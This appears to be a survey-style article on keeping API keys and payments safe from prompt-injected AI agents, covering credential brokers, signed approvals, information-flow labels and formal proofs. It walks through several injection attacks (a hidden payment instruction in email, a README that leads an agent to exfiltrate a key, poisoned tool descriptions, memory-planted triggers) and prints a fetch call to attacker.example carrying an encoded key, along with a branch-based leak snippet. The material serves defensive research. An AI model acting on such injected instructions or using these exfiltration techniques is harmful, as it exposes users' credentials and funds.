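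The extra steps take little computing time. With all components on one machine, a complete SUDP call took 1.21 milliseconds on average, compared with 0.45 milliseconds for a direct call with a bearer token. Repeated calls under a standing grant took at most about 0.52 milliseconds. The tests used a passkey simulated in software, so these figures exclude the delay from a real passkey device and the time a person needs to read and approve a request. For operations that need separate approval, waiting for the person will account for nearly all of the delay.

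### Designs supported by arguments and tests

Jin and colleagues state secrecy as a goal for CapSeal and argue that the design meets it, but don't prove that it does. The goal applies only if the operating system keeps the agent's process apart from the broker's, the attacker doesn't have administrator access, and the broker, policy engine, secret store and audit system all work correctly.

The CapSeal paper also reports tests of a prototype with fixed prompts and scripts. When a prompt asked for an API key, two comparison systems that gave the agent direct access to secrets revealed the key in every trial, while CapSeal never did. In the other security tests, no system revealed an SSH key or made an unauthorized request, so these tests couldn't show any advantage for CapSeal. For unauthorized requests, the reported 95% confidence interval extends to 3.7%, which corresponds to about 100 trials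 per case. The median web request took 0.309 milliseconds through CapSeal and 0.160 without it.

*aiAuthZ* (Kodathala, 2026) places the broker in an authorization gateway outside the agent's machine. The gateway checks who sent the latest user message and whether that person may make the requested tool call. The agent refers to a secret by a named placeholder, which the gateway replaces with the secret only after authorizing the call. This replacement requires an optional mode in which the gateway forwards calls itself, since by default it only returns "allow" or "deny".

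Most of the evidence for aiAuthZ concerns authorization. Kodathala reports that all 58 software tests passed, but the listed subjects, such as signatures, policies and the audit log, do not include the broker. In a live test, a language model attempted four dangerous actions, including reading secrets and sending data to a website, and the gateway blocked all four. No experiment tried to extract a credential from the broker, so the claim that it keeps secrets safe rests on the design.

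Corvic Security Vault stores each credential in a connector, a record that ties the credential to one service. The agent's code receives only the connector's name, and the vault adds the credential to requests for that service. The evidence for secrecy is the 16 successful probes that Kenney and colleagues ran on their own company's product. They recommend independent penetration testing as a next step.

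The team ran two experiments on 27 September 2026, each with one connector, and set the expected security outcome of every probe in advance. In one probe, the agent's code successfully called GitHub without holding a token or supplying an authorization header. This check was needed because a sandbox with no internet access would also have passed the leak tests. When the code called OpenAI's service, the service replied that the request had no authentication. The code also failed to reach the addresses from which programs on Google's and Amazon's clouds can obtain credentials.

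| Design | Status of the secrecy claim | What the evidence is about |
|---|---|---|
| SUDP | Proved by hand, under the assumptions above | A model of the protocol |
| CapSeal | Argued, and tested with fixed prompts | A research prototype |
| aiAuthZ | Argued; the tests concern authorization | A gateway that includes the broker |
| Corvic Security Vault | Tested with 16 probes | A commercial product |

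### The case for hiding the key

The strongest argument for a broker is that its secrecy proof doesn't depend on how the language model behaves, which is true of any proof that treats the agent as the attacker. This is a considerable advantage because models vary widely in how often they refuse attacks. Kodathala tried eight attacks on 15 models, running each attack five times and counting it as refused only if the model refused every time. Among the models that completed all eight, refusal rates ranged from 38% to 100%, and the most expensive model refused only half. A security argument that relied on refusals would need new measurements for every model and every new style of attack.

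A broker also reduces the damage from other mistakes. If the agent's conversation history ends up in a public log, the log contains a useless name instead of the key. If the agent contacts a service without going through the broker, it has no stored credential to send. An attacker may still get the broker to misuse a key without seeing it.

### The costs of a broker

A broker is an attractive target because it holds many credentials in one place. Jin and colleagues acknowledge this for CapSeal and suggest moving the broker's sensitive code into a trusted execution environment. Kodathala states that an attacker who fully controls the gateway's machine defeats aiAuthZ. Kenney and colleagues cite a breach of such a credential store at Hugging Face, which hosts AI models and applications. The company disclosed on 1 June 2024 that someone had gained unauthorized access to secrets that customers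 stored for their hosted applications. The disclosure doesn't establish that the intruder copied or used all of them.

SUDP reduces this risk by keeping the means of unlocking the store on the authorizer's device, but a user who loses every registered passkey also loses access to the stored secrets. Yu and colleagues recommend registering a spare passkey and advise against a master key on the server, which would undo the protection against a storage breach. The passkey must also support the function that produces W, and not all passkeys do.

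Each service also needs an adapter, because services expect credentials in different places. In the vault study, FRED, an economic data service of the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis, rejected a connector's request because the vault put the key in an authorization header instead of a parameter in the web address. No key leaked, but the connector did not work until someone corrected it. CapSeal's approach to SSH similarly requires changes to existing workflows in which programs borrow a user's login key.

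SUDP's security argument also depends on the adapter. Under P1, someone has to identify every detail of a service's requests that affects what those requests are allowed to do, and include it in o. If an adapter for a payment service left out the recipient's account, the authorizer could approve a payment without seeing who would get the money. The proof wouldn't reveal the omission because it assumes P1.

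Services could avoid some of these drawbacks by accepting signatures instead of reusable keys, as Ganesan proposes. Few services are close to doing this. Ganesan cites a survey of 5,205 open-source servers for the Model Context Protocol, which found that 53% relied on static API keys or personal access tokens and only 8.5% used OAuth. For services that accept only ordinary tokens, his design also falls back on a broker that holds the token.

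## Can an attacker still use a key that stays hidden?

Suppose a user asks an agent to pay a window cleaner's invoice for 20 dollars. A broker holds the credential for the user's bank, so the agent must ask the broker to pay. An email the agent reads during the task contains a hidden instruction to send 2,000 dollars to a stranger, and the agent asks the broker to make that payment instead. The bank is an allowed destination and the request is well formed, so the broker adds the credential and sends the request to the bank. The stranger gets the money without learning anything about the credential.

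### The confused deputy

This problem gets its name from an incident that Hardy recounts in *The Confused Deputy*. At Tymshare, a company that sold computer time, a compiler had permission to write files in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there. The company's billing records were in the same directory. A user named the billing file as the destination for debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the records.

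Hardy argues that the compiler went wrong because it had authority from two sources, its own permission and the user's, and no way to state which one it was using. A broker is in a similar position because the credential gives it the user's authority over the bank account, but its instructions come from an agent that reads strangers' text. Surapani and colleagues therefore treat prompt injection as a confused-deputy attack, in which outside content is acted on with the user's authority.

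Hardy's remedy was to replace file names with capabilities, which both identify a file and permit its use. The user could then direct the output only to files they already had the right to change. Rajani, Garg and Rezk prove in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks* that capabilities do not stop every attack of this kind. They call a program free of confused-deputy attacks if, for every protected item, the attacker either cannot affect its final value or could have written that value himself. Capabilities prevent the attack on the compiler, but they do not help when the deputy already holds the right capability and the attacker supplies only the value, as when a web server copies a visitor's text into a database. A broker limited to one bank account has the same weakness, because the agent still supplies the payee and the amount.

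Taken literally, this definition would also forbid the 20-dollar payment, since the agent writes that request too and could not make the payment alone. Rajani and colleagues therefore let a program mark some steps as endorsed, meaning that the deputy deliberately accepts outside influence. Endorsed steps are exempt from the test. For a broker, the obvious endorsement is the user's approval. Whether the payment is safe then depends on exactly what the user approved.

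### Why a secrecy proof permits the theft

The four-rule broker allows the stranger's payment under Call D, which lets the attacker choose any request body b. The proof checks only that the attacker's knowledge K does not grow. Noninterference would not rule out the payment either, because it compares two runs and the bank pays the stranger in both.

Ruling out the theft takes an authorization property, such as those that Yu and colleagues prove for SUDP. An approval identifier, id, makes the earlier authorization formula stricter, because each approval then permits only one execution:

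*For every run: if execute(a, id) occurs at step j, then approve(u, a, id) occurs at some step i < j, and no other execution uses id.*

The action a must be the same in both events. If approve records only "a payment" while execute carries out a particular payment, the formula can hold even in the run where the stranger gets 2,000 dollars.

### Tokens that work only with a private key

*RFC 9449*, by Fett, Campbell and colleagues, defines DPoP (Demonstrating Proof of Possession), a standard OAuth defence against stolen tokens. The program that will use a token creates a key pair, and the server that issues the token ties it to the public key. Every request with the token must then carry a fresh proof signed with the private key. The proof covers the request's method and address, a timestamp, a unique identifier and a hash of the token.

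A DPoP token is therefore not a bearer credential. If an agent prints one in a public log, a stranger cannot use it without the private key. A proof that the private key stays secret could use Paulson's short argument for keys that nobody sends.

DPoP does not stop the payment to the stranger, because the broker signs a valid proof for whatever request the agent induces it to make. Hostile code inside the program that holds the key poses a closely related threat, which Fett and colleagues place out of scope. Such code can use the key without extracting it. It can even create proofs with future timestamps and send them away with the token, unless the service requires each proof to include an unpredictable value that the service chose. The proof also omits the request body. Payments of 20 and 2,000 dollars typically go to the same address with the same method, so nothing in the proof distinguishes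 them.

### Signing the exact action

Agent Step-Up, or ASU, is a gateway that asks the user to approve individual actions. Kodathala, Pollishetty and Cargill (2026), in *Approve What, Exactly?*, built it as a reference defence and analysed its protocol in Tamarin. They name SUDP as the closest earlier design. An action that needs approval takes six steps:

1. The agent sends the gateway a tool call and, if it likes, an explanation.
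2. The gateway, which runs on a separate machine, converts the call into a standard description Δ and computes its hash h. The explanation is not part of Δ.
3. The gateway stores Δ and gives the agent only an identifier, id.
4. The user's phone opens a page from the gateway showing a card built from Δ. The page labels the agent's explanation as untrusted.
5. If the user approves, a passkey on the phone signs the approval.
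6. The agent retries with id. The gateway marks the approval as used and executes the stored Δ. If the agent submits different details this time, their hash does not match h and the gateway refuses.

In the Tamarin model, the passkey signs the tuple

*(tag, h, id, g).*

The tag marks the signature as an approval, h fixes the action, id ties the signature to one approval, and g is the hash of a standing grant if the user also allows similar actions later. The real protocol adds a random value, which the model omits. This omission only gives the attacker more chances to reuse a signature, so the safety results still hold.

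### The Tamarin results

The model treats the agent as a Dolev-Yao attacker. The agent chooses every tool call and every explanation, sees all the gateway's replies and all the passkey's signatures, and can send the gateway any message. The proofs use up to three assumptions: the user decides based on the card, not the agent's explanation; only the user can register the first passkey; and the approval page shows the card that matches what the passkey signs.

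| Lemma | User decides from the card | Only the user registers the first passkey | Honest page |
|---|---|---|---|
| If the gateway executes an action, the user approved that action first | Assumed | Assumed | Assumed |
| If the gateway executes an action, the user's passkey signed its hash for that approval | | Assumed | |
| Each approval leads to at most one execution | | | |
| Someone with only the user's public key accepts a record only if the passkey signed exactly that record | | Assumed | |
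| If that person accepts a record, the user approved the action | Assumed | Assumed | Assumed |
| An action under a standing grant has the approved tool and recipient, and no larger amount | Assumed | Assumed | Assumed |
| A standing grant never exceeds its number of uses | | | |

The analysis has 53 lemmas about ASU and six weaker variants of it. Each lemma turned out to be true or false as the researchers expected. In one variant, the user reads the agent's description instead of a card built from Δ. The passkey still signs the right hash, but the gateway may execute an action that the user didn't approve.

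The team also removed each assumption from the ASU model in turn, and Tamarin found an attack every time. If the user decides based on the agent's explanation, the agent can describe a payment of 500 to the attacker as "send 5 to alice". If registration is open, the agent can register its own passkey for a user who has none, then approve its own requests.

These results apply only to a model of the protocol. The gateway's code, about 5,600 lines of Python, has been tested but not formally verified. The model assumes that two different actions never produce the same card, which the team checked only by testing. The threat model also excludes actions that reach the bank without passing through the gateway.

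### A dishonest approval page

Suppose two approvals are waiting, one for 20 dollars to the window cleaner and one for 2,000 dollars to the stranger. A malicious page shows the card for the first but gives the passkey the tuple for the second. The user reads the card carefully, sees the correct payment and approves. The passkey signs the 2,000-dollar payment, and the gateway executes it because the signature is valid.

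Two lemmas in the table become false: that the user approved the action the gateway executed, and that an accepted record shows the user's approval. The lemma about signed records remains true because the passkey signed exactly that record.

The user can't detect the switch because a passkey device doesn't display what it signs. A bank would later see a valid signature for 2,000 dollars and might conclude that the user had agreed to the payment, though the signature shows only that the user's passkey was used. An authenticator with its own screen could remove the need to trust the page, but the user would have to trust the software that draws on the screen.

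An injected agent cannot carry out this attack alone. In tests, the gateway refused the agent's token at every address involved in the approval. An attacker would have to change the page, for example by getting a malicious script into it. Someone who controlled the whole gateway would not need to deceive the user, because the gateway holds the credentials and could pay without an approval.

### Which fields a 20-dollar payment must bind

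In the honest case, the card shows the window cleaner's account and the amount, the user approves, and the gateway pays. Each field below prevents a different misuse of that approval:

| Field | Approved value | Possible misuse if the approval does not bind it |
|---|---|---|
| Action | One payment | The agent sets up a monthly payment |
| Payee's account | The window cleaner's account number | The agent pays 20 dollars to a stranger |
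| Amount | 20.00 | The agent pays the window cleaner 2,000 dollars |
| Currency | US dollars | The agent pays 20 Kuwaiti dinars, worth about three times as much |
| Invoice | This month's | The payment settles another customer's bill |
| Approval identifier | New for this request | The agent makes the same payment repeatedly |
| Expiry time | A few minutes from now | The agent pays next week, after the user has already paid in cash |

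European payment rules cover two of these fields, the amount and the payee. The payer must see both, and the code that authorizes a remote payment must depend on both and become invalid if either changes. The Tamarin model of ASU does not include expiry, so its lemmas do not rule out the late payment.

The card also has to show the fields in a way that lets the user tell different payments apart. Kodathala and colleagues found that a sample approval card for AP2, Google's payment protocol for agents, displays a name the merchant chooses, while the signature covers the merchant's identifier, so two payees can look identical to the user. In a test of the form that the Model Context Protocol uses to ask users questions, a payment of 10 to one account and a payment of 10,000 to another produced the same request. Both went through after the user's side answered "accept", although the protocol's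 specification directs sensitive questions to a different mode.

Finally, the software must execute the action that the user approved. Kodathala and colleagues could measure this in eight agent runtimes. In four of them, someone with access to the paused run, its stored history or a later processing step could change the details after approval, such as changing an amount from 20 dollars to 2,000.

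Payment protocols can omit such connections even when every message carries a valid signature. In *A Formal Analysis of Agent Payment Protocols*, Jiang, Yu and colleagues (2026) modelled AP2 and three other protocols in Tamarin. They trusted a wallet only for the terms it explicitly authenticates, and assumed that the agent may alter or repeat anything else. They checked, for example, whether a single credential can cause several payments. Across 86 cases, they reproduced 46 known or calibration results and found 40 new inconsistencies, including missing bindings and missing checks on earlier events. For each violation, they added the missing condition to the model and verified the property again. They supported ten findings with further evidence, ranging from attacks on implementations to executable traces based on the specifications.

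### Users who approve without reading

The lemmas about the user's approval assume that the user bases the decision on the card. No theorem about a protocol can show that people do this rather than approve requests without reading them.

A proof can guarantee a limit on how many chances an attacker gets. Suppose a user wrongly approves one harmful request in five, independently each time. With 30 attempts, an attacker is almost certain to succeed. If the gateway locks the agent out after three refusals, as ASU does, the attacker's chance of success falls to 1 − 0.8³, or about 49%. In simulations by Kodathala and colleagues, limits similarly reduced the success rate from 100% to between 45% and 60%. Those simulations used assumed error rates and no human approvers.

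They tested 15 language models as automated approvers, a role that models already have in some deployed agents. The models refused 30% of harmful requests when they saw only the agent's description, and 98% when they saw the card. With the card, they also refused 16% of harmless requests, mostly because the test messages contained placeholder text. These figures don't measure human attention.

A common reply to the objection is to ask users less often by giving agents narrow standing grants. In ASU, a user who approves a payment can also allow similar ones. The gateway then fixes every detail of the approved action except some short free text and the amount, which it caps. The grant covers one tool in one session and ends after a limited number of uses or when it expires. *AIP* (Prakash, 2026) applies a similar idea to agents that delegate to other agents. The first token sets the permitted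 actions, a budget and an expiry time, and verification fails if a later link in the chain would widen those permissions.

If a grant allows five payments of at most 20 dollars to the window cleaner, the two lemmas about grants together imply that the agent can spend at most 100 dollars under it, all of it to the window cleaner. The lemmas don't show that the user owed the money, and they don't cover the free text, which could contain a misleading message.

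Simulations gave mixed results on whether grants make users more careful. One attack tried to redirect a routine email to a new recipient. For simulated users who read the main fields but missed some differences, grants reduced the attack's success rate from 20% to zero. For simulated users who approved 30% of cards without reading them, grants raised it from 30% to 70%, because one careless approval also covered later uses. A separate simulation of fatigue could not show any benefit from grants because none of its tasks repeated a similar action.

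If a policy exempts small actions from approval, an agent can avoid approval by splitting a large payment into small ones. In one scripted attack, ten payments of 50 dollars each stayed below the approval threshold. The attack always succeeded without a limit on the total and always failed with one. ASU's default policy requires a new approval after five actions or 200 dollars within ten minutes, even if a grant would otherwise allow the next payment. Surapani and colleagues list such limits on combined actions among the main unsolved problems in agent authorization.

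## What can be proved when the agent can read the secret?

A broker keeps stored keys away from the agent, but agents still come across secrets. A user may paste a key into the prompt, a tool may print one, or a coding agent may open a configuration file to repair it. A proof that treats the whole agent as the attacker can't show that these secrets are protected.

Researchers respond by dividing the agent into a model and a runtime that carries out every tool call. They assume that the attacker still controls what the model writes, but that the runtime works correctly. The model may know the key as long as the runtime refuses every call that would reveal it. The main question is how the runtime can recognize those calls.

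### Labels and a check before each call

In information-flow control, the runtime attaches a label to every piece of data and updates the labels as data moves. In FIDES, an agent design by Costa and colleagues, each label lists the permitted readers, as described earlier, and records whether the data is trusted. Anything derived from untrusted data is also untrusted.

The runtime can't easily tell which parts of its input a model used, so it assumes the model used everything. It gives the conversation a label that combines the labels of all its messages, and the model's next output inherits that label. Before each tool call, the runtime can apply the earlier rule that data may enter a channel only if everyone there may read it. It can also allow a call with serious consequences, such as a payment, only if the call and its arguments are trusted.

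Suppose a user asks a coding agent why a program won't start. The program's configuration file contains the key `sk-42`, which only the user and a service D may read. The project's README contains an injected instruction.

| Step | What happens | Who may read the conversation | Trusted? |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | The user asks for help | Anyone | Yes |
| 2 | The agent reads the configuration file | The user and D | Yes |
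| 3 | The agent reads the README file, which tells it to send the key to a web address | The user and D | No |
| 4 | The model outputs `fetch("attacker.example/?d=c2stNDI=")` | The user and D | No |
| 5 | The runtime refuses the call | The user and D | No |

The call breaks the rule about readers because the owner of attacker.example is not a permitted reader. If fetching a page counts as consequential, the call also breaks the rule about trust. The base64 encoding doesn't help the attacker, since the runtime checks only the argument's label. The label has to be right, though, because the rule about readers won't stop the key from leaking if nobody marks the configuration file as confidential.

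Neither rule covers the company that runs the model. The runtime sends that company the whole conversation, so the company receives the key once the conversation includes the configuration file. Costa and colleagues assume that adversaries cannot observe exchanges between the runtime and the model. If that assumption is unsafe, the runtime can also apply its policy before each request to the model.

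After step 2, the restrictive label prevents the agent from posting even a harmless comment on a public page for the rest of the conversation. To avoid this, FIDES stores any result with a more restrictive label in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. The model can use the name in later calls, and the runtime fills in the value. When the value is a key, the variable name works much like a broker's opaque reference.

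If the agent needs to know something about the hidden value, a second model without tools can examine it and return an answer of a fixed type, such as yes or no. A policy may then let the main model see the answer despite its label. This is reasonable for an untrusted email, because a single yes or no can hardly carry an instruction, but it is dangerous for a key, because 256 yes-or-no answers are enough to reveal a 32-byte key. Costa and colleagues did not use fixed answer types in their experiments.

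### What FIDES guarantees and a leak it permits

Costa and colleagues state that a runtime with these checks can enforce explicit secrecy. Under their definition, repeating a run's tool calls with a different stored key would leave the same public data. The definition doesn't cover what the attacker learns from the agent's choice of calls.

Suppose one tool takes no arguments and loads a public status page whose visitor log the attacker can read. An injected instruction tells the agent to call this tool if the first bit of the key is 1, and otherwise to do nothing. The call has no arguments, so the rule about readers has nothing to check. Explicit secrecy holds because the same call would have the same effect with any key. But the attacker learns the bit from the log. The rule about trust would stop the call only if the developer had classified loading a status page as consequential.

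### Noninterference for every program in a language

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, prove noninterference for LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents. Its programs can prompt a model, copy or clear the conversation, and run code that the model writes. Every value has a label. (Garby and colleagues also credit FIDES with a noninterference theorem for one fixed agent loop, but the 2025 paper on FIDES defines explicit secrecy instead.)

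Labels are easy to get wrong when a program branches. Garby and colleagues found a leak in CaMeL, an earlier defence in which a model writes a program and an interpreter tracks labels while running it. Their example reveals something about a bank balance. Adapted to a key, it looks like this:

```
tmp = true
out = true
if the first bit of the key is 1:  tmp = false
if tmp:  out = false
if out:  send("attacker", "1")
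```

If the bit is 1, `tmp` becomes false and receives a secret label. The program then skips the assignment to `out`, which stays true and keeps its public label. The final test depends only on public data, so the check allows the message. If the bit is 0, `out` becomes false and the attacker receives nothing. The interpreter misses the leak because it updates labels only for the assignments it executes.

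LLMbda prevents this by halting any program that tries to change public state in a branch that depends on a secret. In LLMbda, this state is the conversation with the model. For example, if a program tries to add a message to a public conversation in a branch that runs only when a bit of the key is 1, LLMbda halts it.

The noninterference theorem has to allow for the model's random answers. Let P(C, e) be the probabilities of the results that an observer may see when program e starts with conversation C. A run that never finishes, or that a label check stops, has no result, so the probabilities may add up to less than 1. The theorem is:

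*If (C, e) and (C′, e′) look the same to the observer, then P(C, e) and P(C′, e′) are compatible.*

Two sets of probabilities are compatible if there is a third set, adding up to at most 1, in which every result has at least as high a probability as in either of the first two. If both programs always finish, each set already adds up to 1, so the two sets must be equal, which is ordinary noninterference.

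The theorem is weaker for programs that may not finish. Suppose a program asks the model to toss a coin, outputs the result if it matches the first bit of the key, and runs forever if it doesn't. Whether the bit is 0 or 1, the program outputs its value with probability 0.5. The output probabilities for the two cases are compatible, because a third set of probabilities that gives 0.5 to each result adds up to 1, so the theorem holds. But the program finishes half the time, and the attacker then knows the bit for certain from the output.

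Garby and colleagues prove a limit on such leaks in a single run. The statistical distance between the two sets of results is at most the average probability of not finishing, which is 0.5 in this example. In CaMeL, a retry loop outside the label tracking restarts failed programs, so an attacker could extract a whole secret by observing which attempts fail. Garby and colleagues put their own agent's retry loop inside LLMbda, where the labels cover it.

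The proof constructs the third set of probabilities from a modified version of the program. The modified version skips any computation that depends on data the observer may not see, returning an empty value instead. Its results can't depend on the key, and it finishes at least as often as the original, so its probabilities are at least as large.

LLMbda programs can also endorse untrusted data, which means relabelling it as trusted. A second theorem shows that endorsement can't expose secrets. Noninterference for confidential data still holds whatever the program endorses, even when the attacker chooses all the untrusted inputs.

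Lean checks both theorems and a third that connects them to the interpreter that runs the agents. The proofs don't cover the code that contacts the model over the network. In the team's experiments, the tools were LLMbda functions acting on a simulated bank account, so a tool that contacted a real bank would add to the code that must be trusted.

### Comparing an agent with one that never obeys

Noninterference rejects some agents that do what their users want. If a user tells an agent to send her calendar to anyone who asks for a meeting, its messages have to depend on private data. In *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection*, Dongol (2026) therefore asks only what prompt injection adds to the disclosures the task already involves.

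Dongol's framework, PlanTERS, covers agents that commit to a plan before reading any untrusted content. The plan is a list of commands for reading data, calling tools, computing values and branching. A trusted interpreter runs the plan, but the model may insert extra calls after reading an injected instruction. A monitor decides whether to allow each call and each read of untrusted data.

The standard of comparison is a reference agent with the same plan, the same monitor and the same starting memory, whose model never obeys untrusted content. A leak between two secrets s and s′ is a pair of runs in which the attacker supplies the same content but observes something different. Relative security is then:

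*If the real agent has a leak between s and s′, the reference agent also has a leak between s and s′.*

The attacker may supply different content to the reference agent. If an injected email makes the agent send the calendar without a meeting request, the agent is still relatively secure, because a genuine request would have revealed the same calendar. If the email makes the agent also send a password-reset code, relative security fails, because no email would make the reference agent reveal the code.

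This definition can be too weak when the secret is a key. Suppose the plan lets a stranger submit one guess at the key and learn whether it is right. For any two keys, some guess distinguishes them, so the reference agent already has a leak between every pair. An injection that sends the attacker the whole key then creates no new leak under this definition, so the agent counts as relatively secure. Dongol, who points out the problem, also defines a stricter uniform version in which the content given to the reference agent can't depend on the secrets.

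### The fence theorem

A fence is a monitor rule that revokes a set of tools when the agent first reads untrusted content. Dongol proves the following theorem, which also holds for the uniform version:

*If the fence revokes every tool that an injection can call, and nothing grants those tools again, the agent is relatively secure, whatever its plan.*

The theorem has several conditions:

- Each injected instruction causes a single tool call.
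- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. It may put the key into a call's arguments, but it may not decide when to obey by looking at the key or at the monitor's responses.
- A refused call has no effect that the attacker can see.
- The attacker sees the content and order of the messages that reach him, but not their timing.
- The run ends. For runs that may continue forever, the model must not keep obeying forever.

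The proof uses the invariant that the monitor refuses all the fenced tools whenever the conversation contains untrusted content. An injected call therefore changes nothing, and the reference agent waits until it is over. The two agents take every other step together, so the attacker sees exactly what the reference agent would have shown in response to the same content.

Relative security doesn't guarantee that a key stays secret, because the plan itself might send it. Another theorem in PlanTERS shows that if the reference agent reveals nothing about the key, neither does a relatively secure agent. An engineer can therefore check the plan as though prompt injection didn't exist, and the result also holds for the real agent.

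Dongol applies the fence theorem to a reported attack on SSH keys. A malicious tool server hides an instruction in a tool's description, telling the agent to pass the user's SSH key to that tool. The runtime loads tool descriptions at the start of a session, so the fence has to take effect immediately. In the model, the fence revokes everything except the tool for mailing the user's chosen recipient. The monitor blocks the injected call, and the user's mail still goes out. Blocking only the malicious server would not be enough, because in a related attack its tool description makes the agent misuse a trusted mail server. The model simplifies the SSH attack by placing the key in the agent's memory, whereas the agent in the reported attack had to fetch it.

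### Why the fence must come before the first untrusted read

Dongol compares three plans that contain the same steps in different orders. The command "lock" revokes the tool for sending messages.

| Order of steps | Result |
|---|---|
| Read email, read secret, lock | The model can send the secret before the lock |
| Read email, lock, read secret | The new secret is safe, but the model can send anything already in memory before the lock |
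| Lock, read email, read secret | Relatively secure against every injection that causes a single call |

The idea of a fence comes from processor design. Some processors run instructions before determining whether the program needs them, and a barrier just before a vulnerable instruction stops that instruction from running early. An agent needs its fence earlier because the injection itself supplies the leaking call, and the model can make that call at any time after reading the injection. The second row matters for agents that start with API keys in environment variables, because those keys are in memory before the agent reads anything.

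### Approving a tool or an exact call

A fence would prevent an agent from replying to an email it has read. A monitor can allow the reply if the user approves it, but Dongol shows that the result depends on what the approval covers.

Suppose the user approves the agent's next message, and the monitor then allows one message with any content. Before sending the planned reply, the model can follow an injected instruction and send the attacker a secret. That message uses up the approval, so the monitor blocks the reply the user wanted to send.

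If the user approves the exact text instead, the monitor blocks any injected message that doesn't match that text. Dongol proves that such an agent is relatively secure against any injection that tries to send messages, provided that the model eventually stops obeying the injection. The agent eventually sends every approved reply and nothing else.

A small leak remains if the attacker can measure time. When the secret equals the approved text, the monitor allows the injected message, which arrives one step early, so the attacker learns whether the two are equal. This is almost useless against a random 32-byte key, but it could reveal a secret with only a few possible values.

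### Twenty-five example agents

Dongol proves or refutes relative security for 25 small example agents. Ten are secure, nine leak, and the result for the other six depends on conditions such as what the attacker can observe. Many of the "secure" results cover only the particular attack in the example. Some of the results concern popular defences:

| Defence | Result | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Marking untrusted text and telling the model to ignore instructions in it | Leaks | In the worst case, the model obeys marked text as readily as unmarked text |
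| Allowing only one outgoing message | Leaks if the model can obey before the planned message | The injected call uses the allowance first |
| Allowing requests to only one web address | Stops the two attacks in the example, but others succeed | The model can request that address only when the secret has a certain value |
| Labelling data but not the choice of branch | Leaks | The secret decides whether the plan sends 1 or 0, both of which are public |
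| A fence, against injected programs that can change the plan's variables | Leaks unless a sandbox discards the changes | The plan sends the secret itself |

Explicit secrecy accepts the agent that sends 1 or 0, even though it leaks in the same way as the status-page example.

The whole development has about 31,600 lines in Isabelle/HOL, the most widely used version of Isabelle. Dongol produced the theorems and proofs with help from Claude Code. Isabelle checked every proof, but people still had to confirm that each formal definition matched the one in the paper.

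### What PlanTERS leaves out

The largest exclusion in Dongol's work is the ordinary agent loop, in which the model chooses each call after seeing the previous result. Such an agent has no fixed plan, so there is no reference agent to compare it with. FIDES and LLMbda both cover such agents.

The framework also excludes tools whose reply depends on the call. In PlanTERS, a call returns only whether the monitor allowed it, and all outside content arrives through separate reads. A search engine run by the attacker doesn't fit this model, because the attacker could read the query, which might contain the key, before choosing a reply.

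Side channels and attacks that misuse a tool without revealing anything are also out of scope. The condition on the model's schedule limits the theorem further. A real model with the key in its context could check the key's first bit and obey an instruction only if that bit is 1. The theorem doesn't cover that model, but a proof that treats the agent as an arbitrary program would.

To apply the theorems to a deployed agent, an engineer must also show that the runtime satisfies their assumptions. For example, untrusted content must not reach the language model before the monitor has allowed the read, and starting a new session must erase everything the language model retained from such content.

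### Secrets and long-term memory

Agents with long-term memory often break the assumption about new sessions. In *Trojan Hippo Bench* (Das, Beurer-Kellner and colleagues, 2026), an attacker sends an email whose hidden instruction ends up in the agent's memory. Nothing happens until a later session, when the user mentions a sensitive topic such as tax. The agent then emails the user's message to the attacker.

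Das and colleagues tested this attack on a simulated email assistant with four types of memory. It succeeded in up to 100% of attempts against Google's Gemini 3.1 Pro and up to 85% against OpenAI's GPT-5-mini, even after 100 harmless sessions. Four defences reduced the success rate to 5% or less in most configurations. The strictest, which the team describes as provably secure, reduced it to 0% in every configuration tested. The experiments concerned personal data, but a key mentioned in conversation could leak in the same way.

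Dongol models a similar attack on ChatGPT's memory. A fence fails if it treats stored memory as trusted, because the attacker's instruction is loaded again at the start of each session, when the agent has its tools again. If the monitor treats loading the memory as an untrusted read, the fence theorem still applies.

### Checking a program before it runs

When a model writes a complete program for a task, the runtime can check it before executing anything. *Guardians of the Agents* (Erik Meijer, 2025) proposes such checks. The checker can examine both sides of every branch, including the assignment that CaMeL's interpreter skipped. But because it must judge the program without the data that will arrive, it may reject programs that would have been safe. This approach also requires the model to write the program in advance, which many tasks don't allow.

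Garby and colleagues use a related method in their agent. The model writes a program and tests it in a simulated world until it works, and then the agent runs it on real data. The security guarantee comes from the labels, not from these trial runs, which find mistakes but prove nothing.

### The cost in completed tasks

A monitor that refused every call would satisfy relative security but be useless. Dongol notes that relative security can't detect this loss of usefulness, because the reference agent has the same monitor and loses the same abilities. One example agent in PlanTERS keeps the user's notes secret only by refusing to send any reply, even an honest one. Engineers therefore have to measure separately whether an agent can still do its job.

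Costa and colleagues did this with AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 office, travel, banking and messaging tasks. The table gives the share of tasks completed when nobody was attacking, using OpenAI's older GPT-4o model:

| Tasks | Ordinary agent without checks | Ordinary agent with checks | FIDES with checks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
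| Slack messages | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Averaged over the four groups, the checks cut the ordinary agent's completion rate from about 84% to 42%. Hiding data in variables raised it to 50%. FIDES did worse on travel because most of those tasks never broke the rules anyway and GPT-4o often used the variables incorrectly. With o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES's average advantage over the ordinary agent grew from 8 to 16 percentage points.

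The checks reduced the number of successful attacks against the ordinary agent from 152 to zero. This result is partly due to the labels, because the researchers marked a data field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it. A real developer would have to label the fields without seeing the attacks first.

Garby and colleagues used only the 16 banking tasks, with three attempts at each. With the GPT-5.2 model, their LLMbda agent completed 75% of them with its checks on. CaMeL completed 67% without its policy checks and 37.5% with them. The samples are small, so the 95% confidence interval for the 75% figure extends about 19 points either way. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks on the LLMbda agent succeeded.

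Part of this performance depends on endorsement. When the researchers removed it, completion fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 65% to 54% with another. Endorsement can let untrusted data influence a payment, but it can't expose a secret.

Better models won't recover all the lost tasks. Many of the banking tasks that FIDES failed ask the agent to follow the instructions in a file, such as paying a bill. The runtime blocks the payment because the instructions come from an untrusted file, just as they would in an attack.

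## What has been verified in real agent software and protocols?

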